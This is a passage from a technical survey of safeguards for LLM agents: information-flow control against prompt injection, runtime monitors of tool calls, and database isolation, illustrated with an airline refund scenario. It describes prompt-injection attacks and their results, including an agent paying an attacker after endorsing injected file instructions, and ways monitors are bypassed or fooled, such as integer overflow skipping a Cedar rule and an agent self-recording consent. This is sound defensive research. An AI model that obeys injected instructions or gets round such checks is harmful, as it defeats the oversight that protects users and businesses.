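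The conversation with the model has a label too. Once the model has read the note, any code it writes in that conversation is untrusted. To avoid this, a program can copy the conversation, ask about the note in the copy, and then discard the copy. Only the answer is labelled U, and the main conversation stays trusted. CaMeL builds this separation into its architecture, but in LLMbda a program can choose whether to use it.

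The theorem has to allow for random model outputs and for programs that never finish. Let x₀ and x₁ be two starting points that look the same to an observer who can see only values up to label m. Let ⟦x⟧ₘ give the probability of each result that this observer could see from starting point x. Then:

> there is an ω, with total probability at most 1, such that ⟦x₀⟧ₘ ≤ ω and ⟦x₁⟧ₘ ≤ ω

If both runs always finish, each run's output probabilities add up to 1, so both must equal ω and the observer learns nothing. If they sometimes fail to finish, a small leak is possible. For example, the program could answer "yes" with probability 0.9 for one secret and 0.7 for another, and otherwise never finish. But it can't answer "yes" with probability 0.9 for one secret and "no" with probability 0.9 for another, because ω would have to total at least 1.8.

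To construct ω, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs, which skips any computation once its label rises above m. Such a run can't depend on the secret, and it produces each visible result at least as often as the real one, so its probabilities can serve as ω for both starting points. Lean has checked this proof and a proof that LLMbda's interpreter matches the mathematical definition. The same interpreter calls the model, so the theorem describes the software that runs. The guarantee still relies on Lean's compiler, on the unproved network code, and on the model's answers following a fixed probability distribution for each conversation. It also assumes that all data sources are part of the program, and in the experiments the bank was a simulation written in LLMbda.

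In LLMbda, a program's failure to finish can still reveal one bit of information. A retry loop written in the language carries its labels from one attempt to the next, which closes CaMeL's second leak. However, outside software that automatically restarted failed runs would reopen that leak.

### What strict rules cost

Most measurements of these systems use AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents everyday tasks and hides attackers' instructions in the data they read. The table shows the share of tasks completed when no attack was present. Randori is an agent written in LLMbda, and the CaMeL figures come from reruns by the two other teams.

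| Tasks | Model | Agent | Flow rules off | Flow rules on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking (16 tasks, three runs each) | GPT-5.2 | CaMeL | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Banking (16 tasks, three runs each) | GPT-5.2 | Randori | Not tested | 75.0% |
| Slack messages (21 tasks, one run each) | Claude Opus 4.7 | CaMeL | 71.4% | 23.8% |
| Slack messages (21 tasks, one run each) | Claude Opus 4.7 | ELBA | 85.7% | 47.6% |

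Turning on the rules lowered the scores of CaMeL and ELBA by 29 to 48 percentage points. Randori seems to avoid this drop, but it enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and can mark untrusted data as trusted. Its lead over CaMeL with the rules off is also well within the margin of error because there were so few tasks.

ELBA's rules made no measurable difference to security against ordinary attacks, because all four models in the main test resisted every injection even with the rules off. Zhou and colleagues then simulated a model that always obeys injected instructions, by having the sub-agent that read each one carry it out. Up to 42% of these attacks succeeded without the rules, depending on the model, and none of the 735 attempts per model succeeded with them. However, the rules reduced the share of tasks that Claude Opus 4.7 completed under attack from 71% to 48%. The value of the rules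 therefore depends on how likely the model is to obey a future attack.

Odersky and colleagues found almost no loss in performance on τ²-bench, which simulates customer service. On its airline tasks, DeepSeek V3.2 completed 58.6% by writing Scala and 57.8% with ordinary tool calls. But the airline functions given to the agent have no Classified values, and cancelReservation accepts any reservation number. The result therefore shows that models can write the required code, but not that they would perform as well under strict rules. TACIT's results on AgentDojo, where the functions do return wrapped data, are mixed. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 59.0% of banking tasks and 52.9% of office tasks, compared with 62.5% and 81.4% in CaMeL's published results.

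In a test involving confidential files, TACIT had no leaks in 131 trials with each of two models. Without the wrapper, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. Both models also completed more of the legitimate tasks with the wrapper.

In *PACE*, Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) check information flows at each tool call instead of in the agent's code. Their system records where each argument came from and blocks paths from untrusted or secret data to an unsafe effect. It also separately checks the call's effects against what the user asked for. They prove that a forbidden flow can't complete at a checked call if the record includes every real link in that flow and the chosen block cuts the path. They say this guarantee is weaker than noninterference.

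The version they tested doesn't always meet those conditions, because it can restore a blocked call when the second check approves it. On a sample of AgentDojo cases, blocking paths alone stopped every attack but reduced task success from 76.8% to 13.6%, which may be why they allowed this. Adding the second check raised success to 65.2%, largely because it restored blocked calls. The second check alone also stopped every attack, with 64.6% success, so the path guarantee added little in these cases.

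### Letting some of the note through

If a customer's note gives a medical reason for cancelling, the airline's agent has to act on it, which strict noninterference forbids. Systems therefore offer controlled exceptions. Endorsement marks untrusted data as trusted, and declassification marks secret data as public.

In LLMbda, an agent could ask a model in a separate conversation to classify the note as "health", "weather" or "other", and then endorse the answer. An attacker who controls the note can choose among only those three answers, which is at most log₂ 3, or about 1.6, bits of influence. This bound doesn't limit the financial loss, because if "health" leads to a $900 refund, the attacker can cause that loss by getting the note classified as "health".

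Garby and colleagues prove that the guarantee about secret inputs and public outputs holds however freely a program endorses untrusted data, meaning marks it as trusted. The airline's payments have no similar guarantee, because a careless model could endorse the whole note. Randori reduces this risk by having the model write its endorsements before it reads any untrusted data. It first tries the plan on an invented account, then runs it on the real one.

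Endorsement accounts for some of Randori's success. Without it, the banking score fell from 75.0% to 62.5% with Qwen3.7-plus and from 64.6% to 54.2% with MiMo-v2.5. Endorsement also allowed the only two successful attacks in 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user asked the agent to make a payment as instructed in a file, and an attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent endorsed the attacker's instructions and paid the attacker. Blocking endorsement stops this attack but also makes the task impossible when the file is genuine.

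Narrower exceptions are safer. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes a system in which trusted code extracts a single value from untrusted text, validates it, and releases it for one argument of one call. A customer's note could supply the reservation number this way, but not the amount or the decision to pay. Before each call, the system checks separately that the protected arguments, the exact effect and the call itself are authorised, so a valid amount cannot by itself authorise a second payment.

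In 400 tests with coding agents, Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorised effects. The agents completed 231 tasks safely. In another 73 tests, the system couldn't parse the agent's output; in 61, nothing authorised the proposed effect; and in 35, the agent's authorised action failed to complete the task. The guarantee assumes that the validators are correct, that the record of influences is complete, and that every effect goes through the check.

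### Trusted data and wrong refunds

Every result in this section depends on correct labels. If get_reservation returns the whole reservation as trusted, the note becomes trusted along with the price, and theorems about the language won't reveal the mistake. Labels can also be lost as a program runs. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL treated untrusted text as trusted once a program inserted it into a longer string. Labels can be lost through a database too. If one agent copies the note into a support ticket and another later reads the ticket as part of the airline's own records, the customer's instructions become trusted data. Santos-Grueiro's system treats such text as untrusted again whenever an agent reads it, but this works only if the record of the text's origin has been kept.

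A program with correct labels can still issue a wrong refund. If a customer who paid $300 is owed nothing, the type checker accepts refund(r, resv.paid) because the amount is trusted and the effect is permitted. It also accepts a program that makes the call twice and pays $600, because the effect set {pay} doesn't record the number of payments. The refund limit introduced at the start would catch the second payment, but it depends on the current state of the database, which these types don't describe.

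Zhou and colleagues suggest adding linear types, which require a program to use a value exactly once, so that a permission to pay could be used only once. The airline would still have to decide when to issue that permission.

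## Checking every call while the agent runs

Whether a refund is within the limit depends on what the database contains when the agent makes the call. A runtime monitor can check this, unlike a type checker, because it examines each proposed call at that moment. This doesn't require predicting what the agent will do later.

### The monitoring loop

The basic algorithm is short:

```
trace = []
for each call c that the agent proposes:
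    state = current values of the facts the rules mention
    if every rule allows c, given trace and state:
        result = run(c)
        trace = trace + [(c, result)]
    else:
        tell the agent which rule c would break
```

The monitor checks rules about the state, such as the refund limit, against the amounts it has just read from the database. It checks rules about order against the trace. Before a cancellation, for example, it searches the trace for an earlier check_flown call that returned false for the same reservation.

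A guarantee based on this loop needs two proofs. One must show that whenever the monitor allows a call, the trace with that call added still satisfies the specification. Induction on the length of the trace then extends this result to the whole run. A monitor that blocked everything would also meet this condition, so a useful monitor should allow every call that the specification permits.

The monitor has to decide whether to allow a call before the tool returns a result, so either the proof must cover every result the tool could return, or no rule may depend on that call's result. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) takes the second approach with its monitor, Agent-C, whose rules can mention the results of earlier calls but not the result of the current one.

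The other proof must show that no effect can bypass the monitor. Security engineers call this complete mediation, and it corresponds to Moon and Varshney's effect exclusivity. One way to achieve it is to give the database password only to the monitor, much as the Airlock holds the agent's credentials.

Bypasses are easy to miss when one call can have many effects. The monitor AgentSpec (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) intercepts the function that carries out an agent's next step in LangChain, a popular framework. If that step runs a Python program, the monitor checks one call, but the program may then open files and contact websites. One of AgentSpec's rules therefore inspects the program's source code for web addresses outside a trusted list. This check can miss an address that the program assembles while running, and Wang and colleagues suggest that data-flow analysis would make their checks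 more accurate. A sandbox that checks each file or network operation as it happens would be harder to bypass.

### What blocking can enforce

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Fred Schneider showed that a monitor limited to watching a run and stopping it can enforce only safety properties. Such a monitor has good reason to stop a run only when the next step would make a violation certain.

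The refund limit is a safety property, so the monitor can stop the run just before a refund that would break it. "Every cancellation eventually leads to a refund" is a liveness property. After a cancellation, the refund could always be the next call, so the run never reaches a point where the monitor should stop it. Stopping the run would itself break the rule, because the run would end with a cancellation and no refund.

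Such a monitor also cannot enforce some safety properties. For example, an agent violates "a refund within seven days" by letting the deadline pass without a refund, so there is no call to block.

Newer monitors handle these rules in different ways. *AgentLTL* (Elkoussy and Perez, 2026) checks a rule during the run only if the rule can be broken in a way that nothing later in the run can fix. It checks the other rules when the run ends. Agent-C also runs a final check when the agent tries to finish. If a required call is still missing, it ends the run with an error status, and its theorem about whole runs covers only runs that end without that status. AgentSpec can respond to an event by making a call itself, which Schneider's kind of monitor can't do. An airline could therefore have it issue any missing refund at the end of a conversation, but this works only if the refund tool succeeds.

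### How the monitors evaluate rules

An AgentSpec rule names an event, a condition and a response. The airline's refund limit could look like this:

```
rule @refund_limit
trigger refund
check exceeds_amount_paid
enforce stop
end
```

The condition exceeds_amount_paid is an ordinary Python function, so it can add up refunds or query a database. This makes the language flexible, but the monitor's decision is only as reliable as that function. Wang and colleagues give no proof that their monitor enforces its rules correctly. The monitor can also respond by asking the user for approval or having the model reconsider.

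AgentLTL uses temporal logic over finite traces, with variables for values such as reservation numbers. Its built-in predicate Before(check_flown, cancel_reservation) compares only the first call to each tool, so an agent that has checked and cancelled one reservation could then cancel others without checking them. The printed definition also evaluates built-in predicates over the whole trace, even inside a temporal operator. Under that definition, the rule "a refund follows every cancellation" would accept a refund that came before the cancellation. A developer can avoid both problems with a custom predicate that accounts for the position in the trace.

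Agent-C translates its rules into first-order logic. Let τ be the trace so far, c the proposed call and Ψ the specification. Agent-C asks a solver, Z3, whether this formula is satisfiable:

> (the trace begins with τ followed by c) ∧ Ψ

Agent-C allows a call if the solver finds that at least one continuation would satisfy the specification. It discards the call if none would or if the solver can't find an answer. The rules can also use read-only functions to query the tools' current state, which would let the airline fetch the total refunded.

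Kamath and colleagues prove that if the trace complies with the specification, it still complies after any call that Agent-C allows. They assume that no other process changes the tools' state, which is false for an airline whose staff also issue refunds.

A continuation that satisfies the formula may also be impossible in practice. For example, the follow-up rule and the refund limit conflict when a customer who has already received a full refund asks to cancel. Agent-C's formula doesn't link the database's future state to its present state, so the solver can assume that another refund will be possible later. The monitor would then allow the cancellation, and the agent would have to issue a refund that the limit forbids.

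### When the facts are uncertain

These monitors treat each fact as true or false, but a fact such as "this file contains private data" may be a guess by a classifier with a known error rate. Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues (2026), in *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents*, calculate an upper limit on the probability that a call breaks a rule, and block the call if the limit is too high. They write their rules in Datalog, a language of if-then statements.

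In their main example, an agent redacts file A, combines it with file B and sends the result to an outside company. File A is sensitive with probability 0.9, file B is sensitive with probability 0.2, and redaction fails with probability 0.1. The agent leaks data if B is sensitive, or if A is sensitive and redaction fails. If the three facts are independent, the probability of a leak is:

> 0.9 × 0.1 + 0.2 − (0.9 × 0.1 × 0.2) = 0.272

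But redaction might fail only when A is sensitive, and never when B is. The probability is then at its worst case, 0.1 + 0.2 = 0.3. A company that blocks calls with a risk of 30% or more would allow this one if it assumed independence, but block it if it used the worst case.

The time needed to calculate the exact worst case grows exponentially with the number of facts. Solko-Breslin and colleagues instead solve an easier problem and prove that its answer is never below the true worst case. The approximation can therefore block calls unnecessarily, but it won't allow a call that the exact calculation would block. The theorem assumes that the input probabilities are valid and that an attacker can't influence how often the classifier or the redaction tool fails.

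In tests on recorded agent runs, the method blocked every call whose worst-case risk exceeded the threshold, and at least 98.2% of the calls it blocked did exceed it. However, the researchers generated the probabilities at random and tested only cases small enough for an exact calculation. The results show that the approximation is close, but not how many real leaks the method would prevent. In long runs, the calculated risk can approach 100% even when each call's risk is small, and the method would then block almost every call.

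### How the monitors compare

| Monitor | Rule language | Guarantee | Overhead | Main result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec | Event, Python condition and response | No theorem | 1 to 3 milliseconds to evaluate conditions | Stopped every hazardous task in a test with household robots |
| AgentLTL | Temporal logic with variables and custom predicates | Checks irreparable violations before each call, but one mode permits overrides | Longer runs in that mode | Compliance rose for five of seven models in that mode |
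| Agent-C | First-order rules about calls and state | Proof that each allowed call keeps the trace compliant | 480 seconds per task, compared with 333 without a monitor | No violations in any test |
| Probabilistic verification | Datalog with probabilities | Proved upper limit on the risk | 0.2 to 1.9 seconds on average | Blocked every call above the risk threshold |

These systems ran on different tasks, so their results can't be used to rank them. Kamath and colleagues made the closest comparison. They wrote the same policies for Agent-C and AgentSpec and tested both on τ-bench, a benchmark of simulated airline and retail customer service. With the open model Qwen3-32B, agents followed the airline policy in 79% of tasks under AgentSpec and 100% under Agent-C. But they completed slightly more airline tasks without violations under AgentSpec, 38.7% compared with 35.8%. On retail tasks, they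 completed 53.3% without violations under Agent-C and 37.4% under AgentSpec. AgentSpec's conditions can be any Python function, so some of its violations may come from how the researchers wrote the rules.

A strict rule can reduce the number of safe tasks an agent completes. In AgentSpec's own household test, it stopped every hazardous task, but the share of safe tasks completed fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. In a test with risky programming requests, its rules flagged 333 of the 422 programs that agents tried to run. Of the 89 programs they didn't flag, 58 belonged to two categories in which the agent's code did not contain the requested flaw.

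### What Cedar's proofs cover

Cedar, the access-control language from Amazon Web Services (AWS), has more thorough proofs than these research monitors. Each request specifies who is asking, what action they want to take, what the action would affect, and further facts as context. Cedar allows the request if at least one "permit" policy applies and no "forbid" policy does.

Cedar's developers wrote a model of the language in Lean and proved theorems about three parts of it:

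- Authorisation: Cedar denies a request unless some policy permits it, a matching forbid policy always overrides a permit, and the order of the policies makes no difference.
- Validation: if the validator accepts a policy, evaluating it on well-formed data can't cause a type error, such as comparing a number with a name. A few other errors remain possible, including arithmetic overflow.
- Analysis: the translation of policies into formulas for a solver preserves their meaning. An engineer can then reliably check, for example, whether a new policy allows anything that the old one forbade, provided that the solver is correct.

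The proofs cover the Lean model, but the program that makes decisions in production is written in Rust. The developers run both on large numbers of random inputs and compare the answers, which gives strong evidence that the two programs agree but does not prove it. *How We Built Cedar* (Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues, 2024) reports that the proofs exposed four bugs in the validator and that random testing found 21 more in various parts of Cedar.

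The theorems also don't show that a policy is right. The Cedar version of the refund limit, for example, forbids a refund when `context.refunded + context.amount > context.paid`. Cedar stores whole numbers in 64 bits. An addition that exceeds the maximum causes an error, and Cedar skips any policy that produces one. If an agent proposes a refund of 9,223,372,036,854,775,807, the largest number Cedar can store, to a customer who has already received some money back, the addition overflows. Cedar then skips the rule and allows the call if another policy permits refunds in general. The bank would no doubt reject such a payment, but the rule would have failed without contradicting Cedar's theorems.

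A safer version puts the limit in the only policy that permits refunds:

`permit (principal, action == Action::"refund", resource) when { context.amount > 0 && context.refunded + context.amount <= context.paid };`

An overflow now leaves no policy that permits the refund, so Cedar denies it.

AWS uses Cedar to control agents in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, its platform for building and running them. Tool calls go through a gateway, which checks each one against the developer's Cedar policies before passing it on. When AWS introduced this feature in December 2025, policies could refer to the user's identity and the arguments of the call. Such policies could cap a single refund at $1,000, but they couldn't enforce the limit on total refunds, which depends on the database. Adding the running total to the call's arguments wouldn't help, because the model writes the arguments and could get the total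 wrong. Cedar's proofs also don't cover calls that an agent makes without going through the gateway.

### What happens after a block

In *The Verifier Tax*, Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026) found that agents finished their tasks safely less than 5% of the time in most settings, even when a verifier intercepted up to 94% of forbidden actions. This seems to suggest that blocking unsafe calls leaves agents unable to do useful work.

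The experiment's design doesn't support that conclusion. The researchers ran two small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, on τ-bench's 50 airline and 115 retail tasks. The verifier was the same model with a different prompt, not a formal monitor. When the verifier rejected three proposals in one turn, the system carried out the last one anyway, though this happened in only 28 runs. The table compares agents that had no verifier to agents whose verifier had the policy's rules in its prompt.

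| Model and tasks | Safe success without verifier | Safe success with verifier | All success without verifier | All success with verifier |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 0.0% | 0.0% | 22.7% | 23.3% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 0.0% | 0.6% | 21.2% | 21.5% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 0.7% | 4.7% | 28.7% | 25.3% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 2.6% | 2.9% | 4.9% | 5.5% |

Safe success was already close to zero without the verifier, so the verifier can't have caused the problem. Its clearest drawback was the extra computation. Designs with a verifier used 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens (the units of text that models process), although part of the increase came from a separate planning step.

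The 94% figure comes from GPT-OSS-20B on retail tasks, where the most common violation was using invented identifiers, meaning ones that came from neither the customer nor the shop's records. In one run without a verifier, a customer declined to give personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, and the simulated shop accepted this as proof of identity. Invented identifiers appeared in 93.7% of the model's retail runs, counting runs with and without a verifier, so the verifier must have missed most of them. The verifier's prompt told it to approve any tool that searches for a customer, and a formal monitor with the same rule would have made the same mistake. Sah and colleagues propose a deterministic check that every identifier comes from an earlier tool result, which is a version of the origin rule.

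Other experiments suggest that agents can recover from a rejected call if the system has them try again, as Agent-C does. With open models, Agent-C can return to the start of the rejected call and generate a different one, so the model doesn't have to reprocess the whole conversation. On τ-bench's airline tasks, the even smaller Qwen3-8B completed 39.3% safely with Agent-C and 12.0% without it. Claude Sonnet 4.5 improved only from 42.0% to 43.5%, but its violations fell to zero. The prompts and definitions of safety differ from those of Sah and colleagues, so the scores aren't directly comparable, but they show that blocking calls doesn't have to prevent useful work.

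A verified plan can also help the agent recover by showing it which steps remain, although Soteria's tests don't separate the plan's effect from the monitor's.

How the monitor responds to repeated violations also affects compliance. Elkoussy and Perez compared two modes on simple arithmetic tools. The milder mode blocks a call with a warning but allows it if the agent immediately repeats it exactly. The stricter mode ends the run after repeated violations of the same rule. DeepSeek-V4-Flash had an average compliance score of 0.60 without a monitor, 0.87 in the milder mode and 0.53 in the stricter one. The score includes credit for required steps, so ending a run early lowers it.

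The milder mode is unsuitable for an airline's refund limit, because an agent could exceed the limit by asking twice. But if the monitor ends the run after the agent has cancelled a reservation, the customer has neither a flight nor a refund. The airline could instead block the forbidden call and pass the conversation to a member of staff.

### False alarms

Users will soon abandon a monitor that blocks ordinary work. According to *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* (2026), formal monitors tested on recorded runs caught most attacks but raised alarms on 29.3% of harmless runs. If one run in 1,000 is an attack, that rate would produce about 293 false alarms for every attack.

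*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) tested general rules about the order of actions on recorded runs from AgentDojo and STAC, a benchmark of attacks made up of calls that look harmless individually. The recordings mostly lacked approvals, timestamps and changes of state. Without them, a rule such as "no payment without approval" can't distinguish an approved payment from an unapproved one. In effect, the rules flagged types of action that are often risky, and a list of keywords would have given the same results.

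False alarms can also come from rules that are too broad. When Wang and colleagues had a language model write AgentSpec rules for a household robot, it turned "do not pour liquids to prevent unsafe results" into a ban on all pouring, including watering plants. An airline can find such rules by replaying recorded conversations and checking what each rule would have blocked. *NOMOS* (2026), which compiles written policies into checks on tool calls, reports that none of the closest systems it compares does this before deployment.

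Better rules won't help if the trace doesn't record the facts they depend on. To record approvals, Kamath and colleagues added a tool called action_confirmed, which only notes in the trace that the customer has agreed. The agent calls this tool itself, so if it misreads "let me think about it" as consent, it can create the record that the monitor requires. An airline could avoid this by having its website record the approval when the customer presses a button.

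## Reasoning about databases, retries and concurrent changes

Even if a monitor reads the refund total just before a payment, the total can change before the payment goes through. An airline runs many agents at once, and its staff change the same database, so another agent or an employee can issue a refund in between. Most of the proofs described so far don't account for this. For example, the assumptions behind He and colleagues' plan proofs can all be true while another program changes the database halfway through the plan.

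### Two correct refunds that add up to $480

Databases group reads and writes into transactions. A transaction either commits, which makes all its changes permanent together, or aborts, which discards them all. Suppose reservation r cost $240 and nobody has refunded any of it. The customer complains in a chat window and also by phone, and each complaint starts a session with a separate agent. Both agents call refund(r, 240), which runs this transaction:

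```
begin
  t = sum of all refunds for r
  if t + 240 <= paid(r): insert a refund row of 240 for r
commit
```

A database's isolation level is how much it hides concurrent transactions from one another. Under a common level called snapshot isolation, each transaction reads the database as it was when the transaction began. If two overlapping transactions change the same row, the database aborts one of them.

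| Step | Chat session | Phone session | Committed refunds for r |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads t = 0 | | $0 |
| 2 | | Reads t = 0 | $0 |
| 3 | Finds 0 + 240 ≤ 240 and inserts a row | | $0 |
| 4 | | Finds 0 + 240 ≤ 240 and inserts a row | $0 |
| 5 | Commits | | $240 |
| 6 | | Commits | $480 |

The sessions insert different rows, so the database finds no conflict and lets both commit. Each transaction satisfies its contract when checked against its own snapshot, because the precondition holds with t = 0 and the total afterwards is $240. But the airline has refunded twice what the customer paid. Database researchers call this write skew. It happens when two transactions read the same data and each then writes something that makes the other's reading out of date.

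The original proof of the refund rule used induction on the trace, with each call starting from the state that the previous call left behind. The phone session instead starts from a state that doesn't include the chat session's refund, so the induction step no longer applies, even though every contract is true.

### Making transactions behave as if they ran one at a time

Serializable isolation rules this out by requiring the committed transactions to have the same result as running them one at a time in some order. In either order, the later refund transaction reads t = 240 and issues no refund, so the database can't let both inserts commit. PostgreSQL still runs the transactions on snapshots, but it tracks which of them read data that others changed. When the result might not match any serial order, it aborts one transaction with an error. The application has to run that transaction again,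 and the new run reads the first refund.

*Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* measured a median time on PostgreSQL 18.1 of 0.68 milliseconds for serializable transactions and 0.19 milliseconds for a single statement that both checked its condition and wrote. Serializable transactions had to retry whenever the experiment changed the target row partway through. The half-millisecond difference is negligible compared with the seconds a language model takes to respond, but retries add more delay if the model has to run again.

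An airline can get the same protection for this one rule without serializable isolation. It could store a running total with each reservation and update it like this:

```
update reservations
set refunded_total = refunded_total + 240
where id = r and refunded_total + 240 <= paid
```

Now both sessions write to the same row, so even snapshot isolation detects the conflict. The proof must also show that the stored total always equals the sum of the refund rows.

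Another option is to lock the reservation's row before adding up its refunds. *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* tested a similar repair for a rule that nobody may delete a stored file, or artifact, while another table refers to it. In all 100 trials, a check inside the delete statement missed a reference that another transaction was still adding. When both transactions first locked the artifact's row, and the deletion then checked for references in a new statement, there were no mistakes in 100 trials. The median deletion time rose from 2.11 to 2.31 milliseconds.

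That experiment used the read committed isolation level, where each new statement sees the latest committed data. A repair that is correct at this level can fail at a nominally stronger one. Under PostgreSQL's snapshot isolation, for example, the same lock would not protect the refund limit. The phone session would wait for the chat session to release the lock, then add up the refunds in its old snapshot, where the total is still zero.

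### Writing the isolation level into the theorem

A proof about a shared database has to say which isolation level it assumes, and for whom. For the refund rule, the statement could be:

If every transaction that writes to the refunds or reservations table runs under serializable isolation, and each one preserves the refund rule when run alone, then every committed state satisfies the rule.

The proof puts the committed transactions in their serial order and applies the earlier induction to that order. It requires every transaction to use serializable isolation, because PostgreSQL guarantees a serial order only among transactions that request that level. If the staff's refund screen uses the default level, read committed, it can break the rule even though every agent uses serializable isolation.

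At weaker isolation levels, the proof must show, for each fact a transaction relies on, that no other transaction can make that fact false before the commit. Computer scientists have used this method for concurrent programs since the 1970s. In the double refund, paid(r) = 240 passes the test if nobody changes payments, but refunded(r) = 0 fails because any other refund makes it false. The engineer can see from this failure where to add a lock.

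Some invariants need no such protection. If every transaction inserts only refunds with positive amounts, all the amounts in the table stay positive however the transactions overlap. Peng and Wu (2026), in *Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems*, draw on database research into coordination avoidance, which covers when an application can preserve its invariants without coordination. Enforcing a limit on a total usually requires coordination.

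Peng and Wu focus mainly on the policies that decide whether an agent may act. In one example, a team has spent 9 of its 10 budget credits, and two agents each transfer one credit from different accounts. The policy engine checks both requests while the total is still 9 and allows both, which brings the total to 11. Because the transfers change different accounts, an ordinary check for conflicting writes does not put them in order.

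Peng and Wu define a correctness condition for this, policy-state serializability. Some serial order must explain the whole run, and in that order every decision must match what the policy says about the state immediately before it. The order must also respect real time, so a request that starts after a refund has finished has to take that refund into account. Peng and Wu's system, MasuGate, has each tool's developer declare which pieces of shared state a policy check or an effect uses, such as "the budget of team 5". It then protects those pieces from the check until the effect commits. Let P be the state that the policy reads, and let E and W be the state that the effect reads and writes. The theorem requires that:

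> P ∪ E ∪ W ⊆ the declared state

If a developer leaves out the team's budget, the theorem no longer applies and the system gives no warning. The theorem also doesn't apply if anyone can change the budget without going through MasuGate.

Peng and Wu ran a test in which 256 transfers competed for a budget that had room for 50. They compared MasuGate with a set-up in which the program looked up the spending so far and passed it to the policy language Cedar along with the request. The Cedar set-up allowed about 81 transfers on average, while MasuGate allowed exactly 50. Cedar's decisions were correct for the totals it received. A single lock around every operation also gave exactly 50, but it makes unrelated teams wait for each other. When each operation included 10 milliseconds of work, MasuGate completed 86 operations a second and the single lock completed 53. With no added work, the single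 lock was slightly faster.

### Checks that go out of date while the model thinks

A database transaction usually lasts milliseconds, but an agent might read a reservation, think for ten seconds, ask the customer a question and get the answer an hour later. Holding locks throughout would stop everyone else from working on the same records, so practical systems let the agent think without a lock and check again when it acts. The designer must decide what that check compares.

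*Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* compares the options on 16 infrastructure operations, such as promoting a data snapshot or revoking a role. In each trial, something changed between the agent's read and its write. Some changes made the action unsafe, such as the snapshot failing validation, while others were harmless, such as a new entry in an audit field. The table shows how often each check blocked an action after a harmless change, out of 1,600 trials per check.

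| Check at the moment of writing | Harmless changes blocked |
|---|---|
| Nothing in the database has changed | 100% |
| The record's version number is the same | 80% |
| The conditions for the action still hold | 0% |

None of these checks allowed an unsafe write under the conditions the researchers had declared. Checking the conditions themselves is clearly best in this comparison, but it depends on the list of conditions being complete. The researchers also tried five hazards outside the list, such as a worker quota that ran out in the meantime. The condition check let all five through, and the version check blocked three of them because they changed the record's version number.

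Version checks can fail when the model supplies the version number. The researchers replayed 3,456 proposals from three small open models and compared the number in each proposal with the record's current version. This check allowed unsafe writes in 4.9% of decisions, because a model sometimes wrote a wrong number that happened to match the changed record. There were no unsafe writes when the software instead used the version it had saved when the agent read the record.

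The wording of a rejection also affects what the agent does next. The models retried the unsafe action 48.2% of the time when they were told only that the version had changed and were shown an old copy of the data. The rate fell to 1.6% when the message included the failed condition and its current value.

Slow human approvals create the same gap. Suppose a manager approves a refund from a shared budget, but another refund uses up the budget first. Rechecking the budget at the end prevents overspending but wastes the approval. In Peng and Wu's test with competing requests, rechecking lost every pending approval. Setting the money aside when the request went to the manager preserved them all, and MasuGate refused competing requests immediately. This extra bookkeeping slowed the prototype. With 64 teams, 12.4% of unrelated transfers finished during a one-second approval, compared with 18.0%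 under rechecking.

### Machine-checked proofs of isolation

*Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies* (Khan, 2026) provides machine-checked proofs for agents that share memory. In its model, an agent reads values, generates its output and then writes. In one example, a user moves a trip from 14 June to 21 June while an agent is drafting the flight booking, and the agent then books the old date. A snapshot doesn't prevent this, because its values are consistent with each other but may be out of date. The system must also check, before the write, that the values the agent read haven't changed.

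Khan wrote the proofs in Verus, an automated verifier for the programming language Rust, as 274 separately checked statements called proof obligations. Of these, 24 show that the programs for detecting four kinds of concurrency error report exactly the errors that meet the formal definitions. Another 40 show that three designs for a shared memory prevent the outdated-booking error, and 84 connect those designs to the Rust code. The proof for one design holds only if every operation writes something, because the design skips the final check for operations that don't. In one test workload, that design let through 3% of outdated-booking errors.

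The proofs rely on two axioms and on the standard Rust lock being correct. They also assume that a model always gives the same output for the same input. Real models don't, although some systems achieve this by recording outputs and replaying them. In Khan's tests, checking before the write added about 8% to the tokens used on one workload and no measurable amount on others. Locking in advance multiplied the cost by up to 1.6 with GPT-4o and 2.3 with Claude Sonnet 4.5.

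Such errors also occur in released software. Khan reproduced one in deer-flow, a widely used agent application from ByteDance. One update silently overwrote another, and Khan proved that a corrected design prevents this.

Storage systems have machine-checked proofs too. *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification* (2026) cites two by Tej Chajed and colleagues. GoJournal (2021) is a journaling system, which makes groups of disk writes atomic even if the machine crashes. DaisyNFS (2022) is a file system on top of a verified transaction layer. Because that layer makes concurrent operations behave as if they ran one at a time, the proof of the file system can assume each operation runs alone, as the theorem about refunds does.

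### When the payment provider's reply gets lost

The refund transaction so far only adds a row to the airline's database. The money moves when the airline calls a payment provider, which keeps its own database and takes no part in the airline's transaction. If the refund tool called the provider from inside the transaction, each session in the double-refund example would pay the customer $240 before trying to commit. Serializable isolation would then abort one of the transactions, and the refunds table would show the correct total of $240 even though the customer had received $480.

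A database can roll back a transaction because it controls every copy of the data and hides uncommitted changes. It does not control the payment provider's records or the customer's bank account, and the customer may already have spent the money. Automatic retries make this worse, because rerunning an aborted transaction repeats any payment inside it.

A lost reply causes problems even with a single agent. Suppose the provider pays a refund, but the connection fails and the agent sees only a timeout. Trofimov and Novikov consider the agent's options. Paying again may refund the customer twice. Recording the refund as complete may leave the customer without the money. Reversing the payment may take back money that never arrived, and giving up may leave a payment unrecorded. They argue that no procedure can avoid all of these risks and still finish the task unless the provider offers some way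 to establish what happened.

Engineers combine several mechanisms to deal with this, and each supports a different property.

| Mechanism | Property it supports | What a proof has to assume |
|---|---|---|
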